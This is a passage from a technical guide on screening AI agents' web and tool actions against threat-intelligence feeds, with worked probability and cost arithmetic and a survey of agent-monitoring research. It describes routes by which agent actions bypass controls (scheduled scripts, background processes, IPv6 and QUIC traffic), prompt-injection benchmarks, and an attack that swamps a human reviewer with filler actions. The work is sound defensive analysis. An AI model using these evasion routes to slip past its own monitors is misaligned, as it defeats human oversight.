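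A blocked agent receives error 502 for a plain HTTP request or 403 for a connector, according to Microsoft's *Configure Global Secure Access, the Secure Web and AI Gateway for agents*. Error 502 normally indicates a fault between servers, so the agent may try the same link again or look for another route to the file. Microsoft calls this a known issue and promises improvements. AgentBouncer adds a note about each denial to the tool's output, which makes the agent more likely to move on to another supplier.

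The exceptions for false matches apply to whole domains, but the feeds also list individual URLs. To unblock one wrongly listed page, the administrator therefore has to exempt every page on its domain.

The service blocks requests that match a high-severity entry and lets the rest continue, so an entry of moderate confidence has no effect. The documented rules also don't make the service stricter with an agent that has just opened a doubtful page. The traffic log records a threat type for blocked requests, but log entries can take up to five minutes to appear, and the agent may have finished its task by then. An operator who wants a graded score has to make a separate lookup, for example at the tool interface. Microsoft lets customers connect an outside security system that examines an agent's planned actions and can block them. Such a system could look up the domain of an email's recipient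 and combine the result with other evidence.

The service does not cover everything a Copilot Studio agent does. In May 2026, Microsoft listed these exclusions:

- Bing searches, including knowledge that the agent takes from public websites and Wikipedia
- requests to Dataverse and Azure SQL databases that serve as knowledge sources
- requests from prompts, agent flows, Computer Use (which operates a screen as a person would) and child agents (which take over part of a task)
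- requests to language models, whether to plan the work or to improve results
- connectors that are missing from Microsoft's list of supported ones, which has more than 40 entries

An operator should check the current list before relying on the service. Some of these gaps matter more than others. Requests to a language model go to a known provider, which is unlikely to appear in a phishing feed. The supplier comparison, however, depends on web search and perhaps on Computer Use, through which an agent reaches unfamiliar sites. Most of the supported connectors lead to well-known services such as Jira or Google Drive, so the feeds are likely to be most useful for plain HTTP requests, custom connectors and outside tool servers.

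For agents that run on an employee's own computer, Microsoft's *How to manage the Internet Access profile* (2026) describes a separate forwarding policy and names GitHub Copilot CLI and Claude CLI as examples. Microsoft warns that the client software this policy relies on does not capture traffic over IPv6, the newer version of internet addressing, so this traffic goes straight to the network. The client also does not support QUIC, a protocol that many websites use in place of ordinary HTTPS connections. Microsoft's remedy is to make the computer prefer IPv4 and to block QUIC in the firewall, after which most sites fall back to a connection that the client can forward.

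### Actions that bypass the check

Gaps like these are common in other controls for agents. *guardscope* (Toyoda, Leung and U, 2026) identifies 15 paths from a model's decision to its effect and works out which of them a control can check from each of several positions. A simple gateway for tool requests is certain to check only one. The permission system of the agent's harness, the program that runs the model and carries out its tool calls, checks five.

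Five other paths bypass every control outside the operating-system kernel:

- operations that the harness's own code performs directly
- requests through a helper program on the same machine
- jobs that the agent hands to a scheduler
- background processes that continue after the tool call has ended
- requests that a tool server sends back to the harness

If an agent schedules a script to run at midnight, the script may download a file when there is no tool call to check.

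The result overstates the problem for destination lookups because the 15 paths include actions that never touch the network, such as changes to local files. A proxy that carries all outgoing traffic should still receive the midnight script's web request, unless the scheduler runs the script outside the proxy's network boundary, where the request can bypass it.

Toyoda and colleagues also tested real controls with a fixed set of 15 actions, using a kernel sensor to record what happened. They replayed the actions without a language model so that every run was the same. When they combined the harness's permission system with a gateway, the two controls checked all seven tool-server calls but none of the other eight actions, which included direct network connections. Adding a second control did not extend checking to those eight actions because neither control was on their route. In a different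 setup, a network rule that denied outgoing connections by default stopped both direct connections. An operator who wants to check destinations should therefore start with such a rule and let only the proxy through.

Kernel controls have broad coverage in theory, but ActPlane, the one that Toyoda and colleagues tested, missed all seven tool-server calls and one network message. The 15 test actions covered only four of the 15 paths, so the results for the other 11 come from analysis. An action counts as "checked" if it went through a control, even if the control made the wrong decision.

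Few agents seem to use feeds, even when they check destinations. Kim and colleagues examined three coding agents and three web agents, all open source. The web agents commonly relied on manually maintained lists of allowed and forbidden domains. All six agents logged their actions for later review, but none searched the logs automatically for suspicious behaviour. Kim and colleagues recommend replacing the manual lists with automatic checks of a domain's reputation, which is close to what a feed offers. They reviewed work up to October 2025 and note that the agents change quickly, so newer versions may do better.

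Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*, found similar gaps among four general-purpose assistants that run on a user's own machine. OpenClaw and Nanobot had no network filtering. IronClaw restricted some tools to an allowlist of permitted destinations but did not restrict every channel. Only NemoClaw, which runs the whole agent inside a sandbox, filtered the network fully. Pirch and colleagues argue that a filter should cover web browsing, email, messaging, shell commands and add-on programs. Otherwise, an attacker whose instructions fail in the browser can tell the agent to use the shell.

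### Local copies, live queries and failed lookups

The operator can download the feed and search its own copy, or send each value to the feed owner's server. A local copy is faster because a search in memory takes well under a millisecond, while a live query has to travel to the server and back. Suppose the round trip takes 50 milliseconds and the agent's supplier comparison involves 800 web requests, most of them for images and scripts on the pages. If the requests ran one after another, live queries would add 40 seconds. If the software looked up only domains and remembered each answer for the rest of the task, 60 different domains would add three seconds.

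Live queries return the latest entries, which a local copy may lack until its next update. But they also let the feed's owner see which domains the agents visit and perhaps infer, for example, that the company is looking for a new packaging supplier. Full URLs are more sensitive because they can contain search terms, customer numbers or a code that opens a private document. An operator who must use live queries should send only the domain where possible, and otherwise remove everything after the question mark in the URL.

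Google's Safe Browsing has used a compromise between local lists and live queries in browsers. The software stores only the first 32 bits of each listed value's hash locally, and it contacts the server only if the hash of a visited address starts with one of these prefixes. There are about 4.3 billion possible 32-bit values, so with five million listed entries, about 1,160 of every million harmless lookups would match by accident and lead to a live query. The server receives only part of a hash in those cases, but it could still guess many of the domains because there are far fewer registered domains than possible 32-bit values.

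Every lookup system fails sometimes, so the operator has to decide in advance whether to allow or refuse actions that the software could not check. In the trial of feed A in the previous example, the agents made a million requests, and the feed listed 27 of the malicious domains they encountered. If lookups failed at random 0.1% of the time, refusing unchecked actions would stop about 1,000 requests, nearly all harmless. Allowing them would let through an average of 0.027 listed malicious domains, or about one domain in every 37 such trials. For ordinary browsing, allowing the action looks like the better choice.

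This calculation assumes that failures are unrelated to attacks, but an attacker may be able to cause one, for example with a URL that the parser cannot read or enough redirects to make the lookup time out. The software should therefore treat a failure caused by a particular address differently from an outage that affects all lookups. It can reasonably refuse an address it cannot parse, since few legitimate sites need one.

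During a general outage, the decision should depend on what the action could do. If a live query fails, the software can fall back on a local copy, even one that is a few hours old. If there is no usable copy, the agent could keep reading public pages but wait before it runs a downloaded program, sends out company data or makes a payment. The price list is a borderline case. The agent could save the file but should not open it until the lookup works again.

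## Turning a match into a score and a decision

A lookup returns an indicator with a threat type and a confidence. The operator still has to work out how likely the action is to cause harm, and whether that likelihood justifies stopping it. Both steps use simple arithmetic that applies to any kind of alarm. The numbers in the running example are invented, because nobody seems to have measured how often a feed match on an agent's action is correct. The studies of agents later in this section tested scores built from other signals.

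### How far a match shifts the odds

Suppose an operator's agents make 1,000,000 web requests a day, and 10 of them go to malicious destinations. The feed lists 5 of those destinations, a coverage close to the best that Deri and Fusco measured for scanners. It also wrongly matches 1 in 10,000 harmless requests. The software therefore finds 5 true matches and about 100 false ones each day, so a matching request has about a 4.8% chance (5 in 105) of being malicious.

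The same calculation works for any feed. Let M be the number of malicious requests and H the number of harmless ones. The feed matches a share c of the malicious requests and a share f of the harmless ones, which gives c × M true matches and f × H false ones. The odds that a matching request is malicious are the ratio of the two:

**(c × M) / (f × H) = (M / H) × (c / f)**

M / H is the odds before the match. The other factor, c / f, is the likelihood ratio, which is how many times more often a match appears on malicious requests than on harmless ones. In the example, it is 0.5 / 0.0001 = 5,000. The odds before the match are about 1 to 100,000, so the odds after it are 1 to 20, again a probability of 4.8%.

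A match is therefore strong evidence, but 20 of 21 matches are still false because the base rate, the share of all requests that are malicious, is so low. If the agents worked on riskier tasks and 100 requests in a million were malicious, a matched request would have a 33% chance of being malicious. If only one in a million were malicious, the chance would be 0.5%.

*The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (Axelsson, 1999) makes a similar calculation for software that searches computer logs for signs of an attack. It assumes two intrusions a day among 1,000,000 log records. Even if the software caught both, 100 false alarms a day would mean that only about 2% of its alarms were real. The paper concludes that false alarms limit such a system more than missed attacks do. The same is true in the feed example. If the feed listed all 10 malicious destinations,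 a matched destination would have a 9.1% chance of being malicious, but cutting false matches to a tenth would make that chance 33%.

The absence of a match is much weaker evidence. Half of the malicious requests and nearly all of the harmless ones don't match the feed, so the likelihood ratio is about 0.5, and the odds that a request is malicious fall from 1 in 100,000 to 1 in 200,000. *LEGION* (2026), a benchmark in which agents investigate security incidents, reflects this with a simulated domain lookup that returns "malicious" or "unknown", but never "safe".

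An operator can estimate the likelihood ratio from a trial. In the invented trial described earlier, feed A covered 45% of attacks and matched 40 of about a million harmless actions, so its ratio is 0.45 / 0.00004, or about 11,000. Feed B covered 35% of attacks but made 8 false matches, so its ratio is about 44,000. At a base rate of 10 attacks per million actions, an action that matches feed A would have about a 10% chance of being an attack, and one that matches feed B about a 30% chance, so a match in B is the more reliable warning even though B catches fewer attacks.

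One ratio for a whole feed is often too crude. Suppose fresh, high-confidence entries produce 4 of the 5 true matches in the running example but only 10 of the 100 false ones. A match on one of these entries would have a 29% chance of being true, while a match on any other entry would have about a 1% chance. An operator who regularly reviews matches can calculate these percentages from the results of those reviews, without knowing the base rate.

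### When two feeds list the same domain

Suppose a second feed also lists the domain. If it has the same error rates and makes its errors independently, the operator can multiply by 5,000 again. The odds rise from 1:20 to 250:1, a probability of about 99.6%. But if the second feed copies its entries from the first, its match was certain once the first feed matched, so the probability remains 4.8%.

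The table shows what happens to the first feed's 105 daily matches in these two cases and in one between them.

| Relationship between the feeds | True matches in both | False matches in both | Probability that a double match is malicious |
|---|---|---|---|
| Independent | 2.5 | 0.01 | 99.6% |
| The second feed repeats a tenth of the first feed's false matches | 2.5 | 10 | 20% |
| The second feed is a copy | 5 | 100 | 4.8% |

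Even a modest number of shared errors removes most of the value of a second match. Galloway and colleagues found that a few vendors redistribute much of the material that others use, so one vendor's error can appear in several feeds. Feeds can also make the same mistake independently, for example when two suppliers see the same attack and both list a content delivery network's address.

To find the right figure, the operator can count how many of the first feed's reviewed false matches also appear in the second. Until there are enough reviewed matches, it's safer to use only the strongest match. The same applies to a URL and its domain when both come from one report, and to an agent that requests the same page ten times.

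### The probability at which blocking pays

A probability of 4.8% does not settle whether to block. That also depends on what a mistake in either direction would cost.

Let p be the probability that the action is malicious. If the operator blocks it, the expected cost is (1 − p) × the cost of a wrong block. If the operator allows it, the expected cost is p × the cost of the harm. Blocking is cheaper when p is greater than:

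**cost of a wrong block / (cost of a wrong block + cost of harm)**

Suppose the agent wants to read a page. A wrong block does 1 unit of harm, because the agent has to find another supplier, and a malicious page would do 5. The threshold for blocking is 1 / 6, or about 17%, so the operator should let the agent read the page if the match implies a 4.8% chance that the domain is malicious. If the agent wants to upload a customer file to the same domain, a wrong block might still do 1 unit of harm, while a malicious domain would do 1,000. The threshold falls to 1 / 1,001, or about 0.1%, so the operator should block the upload on the same match.

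The fake wholesaler's page is different because its entry is recent and has a confidence of 85. If such entries are right 29% of the time, as in the split above, the operator should block even a page view.

Without a match, the odds of harm are about 1 in 200,000, so allowing an upload that could do 1,000 units of harm has an expected harm of only 0.005 units. But if the upload could do 200,000 units of harm or more, the operator should block it even without a match, unless other evidence suggests it is safe.

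The costs are judgments, and their meaning depends on whether the operator counts errors per action or as rates. *Trust No Tool* (2026) scores defences for agents with a formula that compares the share of malicious calls accepted with the share of normal calls rejected. It gives accepting malicious calls a cost factor of 1.5, which it describes as an assumption. In the running example, one accepted malicious request is a tenth of all malicious requests, while one rejected normal request is about a millionth of all normal ones. With the formula's other terms included, one missed attack counts about 133,000 times as much as one wrong block. An operator should therefore set costs per action, as above, or convert them before using a formula based on rates.

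Some systems limit the rate of harm instead of weighing costs. *CORA* (2026), which controls agents that operate phone apps, sets a threshold on the risk score to limit the expected rate of harmful actions that run without a person's involvement. The base rate in the running example is so low that allowing every request would lead to harm in only 0.001% of cases. A limit of 0.1% would therefore never block anything, and an operator would need a much stricter one.

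### Logging, removing credentials and asking a person

An operator has other options besides simply allowing or blocking an action. The software can allow the action and log the match, which prevents nothing at the time but supplies the reviewed cases needed to estimate likelihood ratios. It can also open the page in a fresh browser session without passwords, cookies or access to company files, or pause the agent and ask a person whether to proceed.

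The next table compares the expected losses after a 4.8% match. In this example, removing credentials causes a loss of 0.1 when the page is harmless, because the agent cannot see a customer's own prices, and prevents 80% of the harm when the page is malicious. Asking a person causes a loss of 0.3 in time. The person approves 10% of malicious actions and refuses 5% of harmless ones. These figures are also invented.

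| Action | Cost of harm | Allow and log | Remove credentials | Ask a person | Block |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read a page | 5 | 0.24 | **0.14** | 0.37 | 0.95 |
| Send a quote form with company details | 50 | 2.38 | Little help | **0.59** | 0.95 |
| Upload a customer file | 1,000 | 47.6 | Little help | 5.11 | **0.95** |

Removing credentials gives the lowest expected loss for the page view, but it does not help with the form or the file, since the attacker wants what the agent is sending. Asking a person makes most sense for the form. For the customer file, blocking is better than asking, because a reviewer who approves one malicious upload in ten is too unreliable when the harm is so large. Asking would have a lower expected loss only if the reviewer approved fewer than about one malicious upload in 80.

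Reviewers also become less reliable as requests pile up. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (Turan, 2026) simulates a reviewer who catches every dangerous action until the number of reviews reaches a set capacity, then loses two percentage points of reliability with each further review, down to 20%. With a capacity of 25, 57% of dangerous actions got through when the software referred all 125 test actions to the reviewer, but 42% when it referred only 64% of them. If a reviewer with a capacity of 50 had to check all 105 daily matches in the running example, reliability would fall to 20% by the 90th.

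Turan assumed this decline and did not measure it on people, so the exact numbers mean little. The test actions were also deliberately difficult, and the software's own scores were poor at separating safe actions from dangerous ones. Still, the simulation is a good reason to save the reviewer for cases like the quote form. It also shows how an attacker could exploit a system that refers too many actions to the reviewer. When the software referred 88% of routine actions, 50 harmless filler actions were enough to get a malicious one approved 40% of the time, but the same attack failed when it referred 26%.

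### Four ways to combine a match with other evidence

The simplest method is a fixed rule that always stops the action when a certain kind of match occurs. *AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026) describes a system of this type with 170 rules, most of them patterns for dangerous commands and settings. If several rules apply, the system uses the most severe verdict. The check takes a few milliseconds, the operator can see exactly which rule caused a block, and harmless-looking evidence cannot cancel a serious warning. But several weak warnings never add up to a strong one, and a rule written for page views may be far too lenient for uploads.

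AgentTrust gave the right verdict in 96.7% of 630 test scenarios, although Yang had added rules after seeing where it failed. About 55% of the scenarios were attacks, so this accuracy is a poor guide to performance in ordinary use. A rule set that wrongly stopped 1% of harmless actions would raise 10,000 false alarms a day for an operator handling a million harmless requests.

Another method assigns points to each signal and adds them up, like the weighted sum in NIST's design. *MCPThreatHive* (2026) does this for classes of threats to agents' tool connections. It adds four weighted factors, multiplies the sum by up to 1.20 for each of several features that make an attack worse, and calls a result of 9 or more out of 10 "critical". Adding points is easy to explain and adjust, but the points usually have no fixed meaning, so a score of 7 could correspond to a probability of 1% or 50%.

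The operator can solve this problem by using the logarithm of the likelihood ratio as the points. Adding logarithms is the same as multiplying the ratios, so the total always corresponds to a probability. In the running example, with logarithms to base 10, the points are:

| Item | Points |
|---|---|
| Starting score (odds of 1 to 100,000) | −5.0 |
| Match in the feed | +3.7 |
| No match in the feed | −0.3 |
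| Score after one match | −1.3 |
| Threshold for blocking a page view | −0.7 |
| Threshold for blocking a customer upload | −3.0 |

As before, the score of −1.3 is below the threshold for the page view and above the threshold for the upload. This version still counts copied evidence twice unless the operator corrects for it.

With enough data, the operator can instead fit a model that produces calibrated probabilities, so that about 5% of the actions scored at 5%, for example, turn out to be malicious. *NEXUS* (2026) does this for agents' plans, using logistic regression on nine features such as the plan's length and the number of irreversible steps. A correction fitted on separate data reduced the average gap between predicted and actual frequencies to less than a sixth of its original size. Logistic regression can also account for overlap between feeds, which the operator would otherwise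 have to work out by hand.

However, the training data came from 428 synthetic plans, and a score calibrated at one base rate is not calibrated at another. Suppose half the cases in a benchmark are attacks and a calibrated score gives an action a 99% probability of being an attack. The evidence then has a likelihood ratio of 99. If only 10 in a million actions were attacks, the same evidence would imply a probability of about 0.1%.

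A learned model can also take into account the whole history of a task. *DreamGuard* (2026) predicts what will follow from an agent's next action, estimates the immediate danger, and combines that estimate with the risk from earlier steps. It has a lower threshold for holding an action and a stricter test for blocking it, both set on harmless runs. The operator therefore does not need examples of attacks to limit how many harmless tasks the system interrupts. But this limit does not show how often an alarm is right, and it is harder to check why the model flagged an action than to check a rule.

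DreamGuard combines risks with a method called noisy-or, which would also work poorly for feed matches. In its simplest form, it multiplies the chances that each risk is absent and subtracts the result from 1. Two matches of 4.8% would then give 9.3%, but the right answer is 4.8% if one entry is a copy of the other and 99.6% if the two are independent.

*GuardSec* (2026) describes a fraud checker for people rather than agents. Its model combines the result of a reputation lookup with a site's registration record, certificate and other features. When a lookup fails, the software fills in zeros, so a failure may count as a clean result.

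Most operators could sensibly start by always blocking matches to a short list of recent, high-confidence entries and assigning logarithmic points to all other matches. A calibrated model needs reviewed cases, and an operator who reviewed all 105 matches a day would have only about 150 true ones after a month.

### What a skill can do and what a request makes it do

The base rate can differ between actions. An agent that can run code and send emails has more ways to cause harm than one that only reads pages, even before it acts. *STARS* (Zhang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) separates this general risk from the risk of a specific request. The paper studies skills, installable packages of instructions and code that give an agent a new ability.

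STARS first calculates a static prior from the skill's permissions and source. Permission to run code counts for more than permission to send email, and an unverified source counts for more than an official one. It then scores the specific request using five signals:

- risky or destructive wording in the user's request
- sensitive data or outside recipients in the arguments
- how trustworthy the earlier tool outputs are
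- risk that has built up over previous steps
- whether untrusted content flows into a dangerous action, such as running code or sending a message

An email skill has the same static prior whether it sends an order to the real wholesaler or a price list to an attacker. The request score should be higher in the second case, especially if the address came from a review the agent had just read. STARS computes a weighted sum of the two scores, with default weights of 0.55 and 0.45, and uses the result to allow the action, refer it for review or block it.

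STARS does not use threat-intelligence feeds. If an operator added them, a match on the skill's package or publisher would belong in the static prior and a match on a destination in the request score.

Zhang and colleagues tested the system on prompt injections, which they had left out of the training data. Of 450 test cases, 164 were high-risk. Among the 45 cases with the highest combined scores, 25 were high-risk, compared with about 16 in a random selection. On familiar kinds of attack, 9 of the top 45 cases were high-risk, about the same as with the static prior alone. The request score therefore helped mainly with prompt injection, where a harmless skill does something dangerous because of what the agent has read. The targets came from assigned labels and a scoring formula, not from observed harm.

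The choice of thresholds mattered more than these gains. Zhang and colleagues compared two threshold settings that ranked the prompt-injection cases equally well. The lenient setting blocked no harmless requests and let the agent complete 89% of tasks, but caught only 16% of the risky requests. The strict setting caught 52%, but blocked 34% of the harmless requests and reduced task completion to 51%. An operator who improves the score but leaves the thresholds at their defaults may see little benefit.

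### Risk that builds up over a task

Each action in a task can look acceptable while the sequence does damage. *RATION* (Du, Chaudhari and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an injected log entry that makes an agent restart a service repeatedly. The agent has permission for every restart, but together the restarts keep the service offline.

RATION sets limits before the task begins. A language model extracts explicit limits from the user's request, such as the permitted recipient of an email or a maximum payment. It also assigns the task to a category that has a list of usual tools and records of past runs. RATION uses these records to find the level that 95% of runs stayed within for the number of tool calls, the number of calls that change something or contact a third party, and the amount of text the model processes.

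RATION blocks a call that breaks an explicit limit or uses an unlisted tool. When a running total exceeds its limit, RATION holds the call and prompts the agent to reconsider. It then raises that limit by half so that a long but legitimate task can continue.

Without RATION, between 39% and 63% of attacks succeeded across four benchmarks. With it, at most 1.4% succeeded on three of them and 16.5% on the hardest. Most of the reduction probably came from the explicit limits. On AgentDyn, the only benchmark where Du and colleagues tested each part on all tasks, explicit limits alone reduced successful attacks from 53.7% to 9.1%. Adding the list of tools lowered the rate to 5.9%, and adding the accumulated quantities lowered it to 1.4%. Adding the accumulated quantities also reduced the share of tasks completed under attack from 63.6% to 57.3%.

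RATION does not use feeds either, and its three quantities measure unusual activity instead of known threats. An operator could add a running total of expected harm from feed matches. In the running example, reading a matched page has an expected harm of 0.24. With a budget of 0.5 per task, an agent could read two matched pages, but the software would hold the request for a third. The software should count each domain only once, or a page with 50 images on one matched domain would use up the budget immediately.

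*Tail-risk-aware Agent Safety* (Pan, Tian and colleagues, 2026) describes TAS, a system with a similar budget, set by default to 20 points for a whole task. Fixed rules assign points to each action, and a language model's judgment adjusts them. Under the rules, reading an outside page scores 0.5 × 0.8 × 1.8 = 0.72, where the factors stand for a low-risk tool, a read-only action and an outside address. Uploading a file to an outside address scores at least 12 × 1.8 × 1.8 = 38.9, nearly twice the default budget. Before each step, TAS samples 200 possible outcomes and compares the average of the worst ones with the remaining budget.

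The rules check only whether an address is inside or outside the company, so they give the real wholesaler and the fake one the same score. A feed could distinguish the two.

### How noisy the other signals are

Pan and colleagues report error rates for TAS and several other defences on AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants prompt injections in the data an agent reads. They call the figures false positive and false negative rates. But the "false positive rate" for each defence is exactly 100% minus the share of tasks completed, and the "false negative rate" is the share of attacks that succeeded. Even the agent without any defence has a false positive rate of 43%, although it flags nothing. The figures make more sense under their plain names:

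| Defence (agent based on GPT-4o) | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks not completed | Change in uncompleted tasks, in percentage points |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 47.5% | 43.3% | |
| Progent | 46.5% | 37.3% | −6 |
| DRIFT | 15.8% | 69.4% | +26 |
| Firewalls | 12.7% | 47.2% | +4 |
| GuardAgent | 5.0% | 65.1% | +22 |
| Sentinel | 5.0% | 89.8% | +47 |
| TAS | 3.9% | 36.7% | −7 |

Some defences prevented most attacks but also kept the agent from completing much of the user's work. Sentinel stopped about nine in ten of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded, but the agent completed only one task in ten. TAS avoided this trade-off in its developers' own test. Results also depend heavily on the setup. When Du and colleagues tested Progent on the same benchmark with GPT-4.1, it reduced the attack success rate from 62.5% to 7.1%, but it had almost no effect in Pan and colleagues' test.

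None of these figures is a likelihood ratio, because an agent can fail a task for reasons unrelated to the defence. *LatentRiskBench* (2026) measures false positives more cleanly by pairing risky runs with similar harmless ones and counting how often a defence does anything other than allow the harmless run. By that measure, an agent without a defence would have a false positive rate of zero.

*Influence Is Not Authority* (2026) comes closer to measuring a single signal. It tests scores that measure how strongly outside content influenced an agent's action, because strong influence might indicate a prompt injection. When the threshold was high enough to flag none of the authorised actions, the score caught 12 of 48 unauthorised actions with one model and 18 of 48 with another. Legitimate work often depends on outside content too, such as a price from a supplier's page, so strong influence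 alone is poor evidence of an attack.

With so few test cases, the true false-alarm rate could still be several percent. If it were 5%, a signal that catches 25% of attacks would have a likelihood ratio of 5, compared with 5,000 for the feed match. On its own, the signal would raise the odds of an attack from 1 in 100,000 to 1 in 20,000, which is too low to justify blocking a page view. After a feed match, it would raise the probability from 4.8% to 20%, if the two signals are independent. That exceeds the 17% threshold, so the operator should block the page.

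## Handling old entries and late listings

The calculations so far treated a feed's error rates as fixed, but these rates change as attackers move and entries age. If the feed lists an indicator too late, the agent reaches a malicious destination without a match. If the indicator stays too long, the destination may now have a harmless owner, and the software raises the risk score of a harmless action. Deleting old entries reduces these false matches but does not restore the coverage lost to late listings.

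Researchers have measured both faults on ordinary networks, mostly with human victims. Nobody seems to have measured them on agents' traffic, so the advice below on cached results, long tasks and saved links is inferred from how agents work.

### How long feeds take to list an attack

Feeds may contain nothing about attacks on a software vulnerability for weeks after it becomes public. In *Investigating the Temporal Dynamics of Cyber Threat Intelligence*, Kodituwakku, Xu and colleagues (2024) tracked six critical vulnerabilities from 2023 in data from 16 providers, whose names they had to withhold. They recorded when the providers listed related IP addresses and domains, relative to the day each vulnerability appeared in CVE, the public catalogue of such flaws.

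| Vulnerable product | Days until the first listings | Share listed at first | Eventual number of indicators |
|---|---|---|---|
| MOVEit Transfer | 30 | 44% | 149 |
| Ivanti Endpoint Manager Mobile | 12 | 78% | 23 |
| Barracuda Email Security Gateway | 7 | 38% | 31 |
| Axis License Plate Verifier | 3 | over 68% | 16 |
| Metabase | 2 | over 79% | 63 |
| PaperCut | 2 | 39% | 18 |

(The paper gives eight days for Barracuda, but the dates it reports are seven days apart.) MOVEit Transfer, a file-exchange program, had the slowest start. Five days after the first listings, the share had risen from 44% to 98%, and the last few addresses took another 24 days to be listed.

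These figures only approximate listing delays, which start when an address is used maliciously. Attackers sometimes exploit a flaw before it becomes public, which would make the true delay longer. They may also have started using some of the addresses weeks later, which would make it shorter. The percentages are shares of what the 16 providers eventually listed, so even 100% could leave out addresses that none of them found.

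Four of the five authors work for the security vendor Centripetal, and their advice to combine many providers and update constantly suits its business. Six cases are also too few to establish a typical delay, but they do show that a missing match means even less than usual in the weeks after a major disclosure.

### How long phishing pages last

For phishing, a delay of hours is enough to miss most of the victims. Oest, Zhang and colleagues (2020), in *Sunrise to Sunset*, studied pages that imitated one large financial company. Many of these pages loaded images or scripts from the company's servers, which let the company count 4.8 million visitors between October 2018 and September 2019.

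The average attack lasted 21 hours from the first victim's visit to the last. Anti-phishing organisations detected it nine hours after the first visit, and browser warnings took another seven hours to peak. About 38% of the visits came after detection, so even a feed that listed every page at the moment of detection would have been too late for the other 62%.

Many phishing pages go offline soon after somebody reports them. For *7 Days Later*, Lee, Lim and colleagues (2025) revisited 286,237 phishing links every 30 minutes. Half were offline within 5.46 hours of appearing on the list of the Anti-Phishing Working Group (APWG), an industry association. The mean time online after listing was 54 hours because a minority lasted for weeks. The study measured only from the listing, so the pages' full lifetimes were longer.

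Google Safe Browsing listed only 18.4% of these links, and about 84% of those listings came after the page had gone offline, so Google's list contained only about 3% of the pages while they were still online. Chrome blocked far more in LayerX's test, 47 of 100 pages. One likely reason is that LayerX took its pages from public lists, whereas Google is not a member of APWG and cannot see its data.

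Other studies give different lifetimes, partly because they measure different things. In *INFERMAL* (2025), researchers selected 768 phishing domains for complaints to registrars, the companies that sell domain names. These domains stayed up for an average of 70 minutes after they were selected. Domains that the researchers did not report lasted 61 minutes, so the complaints made little difference. *Registration, Detection, and Deregistration* (Lim, Mok and colleagues, 2025) looked at domain names instead of pages. Among names that attackers registered themselves, the median time from registration to detection was 16.3 days. Attackers may hold a name before using it, so the typical listing delay was probably shorter. Domains remained registered for an average of 11.5 days after detection, during which an attacker could put up another page.

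Most of the human victims in Oest and colleagues' study arrived in a wave after an email campaign. An agent that finds a link in search results or an old message may visit at any time, so we cannot tell from these studies what share of an agent's visits would happen before a feed lists the link.

### Which indicators go stale

A file hash identifies exact content. Datadog points out that if a file really is malware, its hash remains a correct indicator permanently. An operator might still remove old hashes to save space. *Decaying Indicators of Compromise* (Iklody, Wagener and colleagues, 2018) notes that some detection software cannot handle millions of them.

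A malicious domain can become harmless when the owner of a hacked site cleans it up, or when an attacker lets a name expire and somebody else registers it. *Short Message Service (SMS) Phishing Attacks and Defenses* (2026) describes a check of 50 websites selected from old collections of malicious text messages. Nearly all of the sites were benign by then. The sample is small and comes from research data rather than a maintained feed, but an operator who imported such a collection as a blocklist would get mostly false matches.

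IP addresses change hands fastest, because cloud companies and internet providers reassign them to new customers. *On the Dynamics of IP Address Allocation and Availability of End-Hosts* (2010), a two-month study, found that over 60% of the computers kept one address, while some of the others changed theirs regularly, with a median period of 24 hours. It warns that many blocklist entries could be invalid after a day. The data are old and cover users' computers, so they apply more to the addresses of visitors to a company's site than to those of the servers an agent contacts.

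One stale address can also affect several sites. *The Web is Still Small After More Than a Decade* (2020) found that almost half of the blocklisted addresses it examined hosted a single domain and the rest hosted more. Lee and colleagues found that 99.8% of the IP addresses linked to phishing pages belonged to content delivery networks and similar shared services, so an entry for such an address can cause false matches even before it goes stale.

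Some entries are listed so late that they are already stale. Netresec's *Optimizing IOC Retention Time*, a November 2025 blog post by a maker of network-analysis software, cites a study in which 90% of the servers that controlled a type of botnet lasted less than five days. It also cites the threat-intelligence vendor Recorded Future, which found such servers an average of 33 days before other sources reported them. Recorded Future has an interest in showing that its rivals are slow. If both figures applied to the same servers, most would be gone before those sources listed them, and the entries could produce only false matches.

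### What an old feed does to the decision

Suppose the operator in the running example stops updating its feed. The feed used to match five of the agents' 10 malicious requests a day, but four of those five destinations have since moved to new addresses. Ordinary businesses have taken over some of the old addresses, and the agents' visits to them add 100 false matches to the usual 100.

The software now finds 1 true match and 200 false ones each day, so the probability that a matching request is malicious falls from 4.8% to about 0.5%. The likelihood ratio falls from 5,000 to 500 because true matches are a fifth as common as before and false ones are twice as common.

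With the same invented costs as before, the best response changes for all three actions:

| Action | Best response at 4.8% | Best response at 0.5% | Expected loss of the old response at 0.5% | Expected loss of the new response |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read a page | Remove credentials | Allow and log | 0.10 | 0.02 |
| Send a quote form with company details | Ask a person | Allow and log | 0.37 | 0.25 |
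| Upload a customer file | Block | Ask a person | 1.00 | 0.85 |

The upload is a close call, but an operator with no reviewer available should still block it, because the 0.5% probability exceeds the 0.1% threshold for blocking rather than allowing it.

If the operator deleted the entries for the addresses that had changed hands, about 1% of matches (1 in 101) would be true. The feed would still miss nine malicious requests a day instead of five, which only new entries can correct.

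### A score that fades with age

Instead of trusting an entry fully until the day it expires, software can reduce its score gradually. Iklody and colleagues proposed a formula for MISP, an open-source platform on which organisations share indicators:

**score = base × (1 − (t / lifetime)^(1 / speed))**

The base is a starting score from 0 to 100, and t is the time since the last sighting. The lifetime is the age at which the score reaches zero. The speed determines how much of the score disappears early.

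An entry with a base score of 80 and a lifetime of 30 days has used a quarter of its lifetime after 7.5 days. At speed 1, its score is then 80 × (1 − 0.25) = 60. At speed 2, the exponent is 1/2, so the score is 80 × (1 − √0.25) = 40. At speed 0.5, the exponent is 2, so the score is 80 × (1 − 0.25²) = 75. The score reaches zero on day 30 at all three speeds.

Iklody and colleagues also considered exponential decay, in which the score loses the same proportion every day. They rejected it because the score always falls fastest at the start and because a single number controls both the shape of the curve and how long the score lasts. They argued that an IP address should keep most of its score during the first hours, when the attacker is probably still using it, and lose it faster later.

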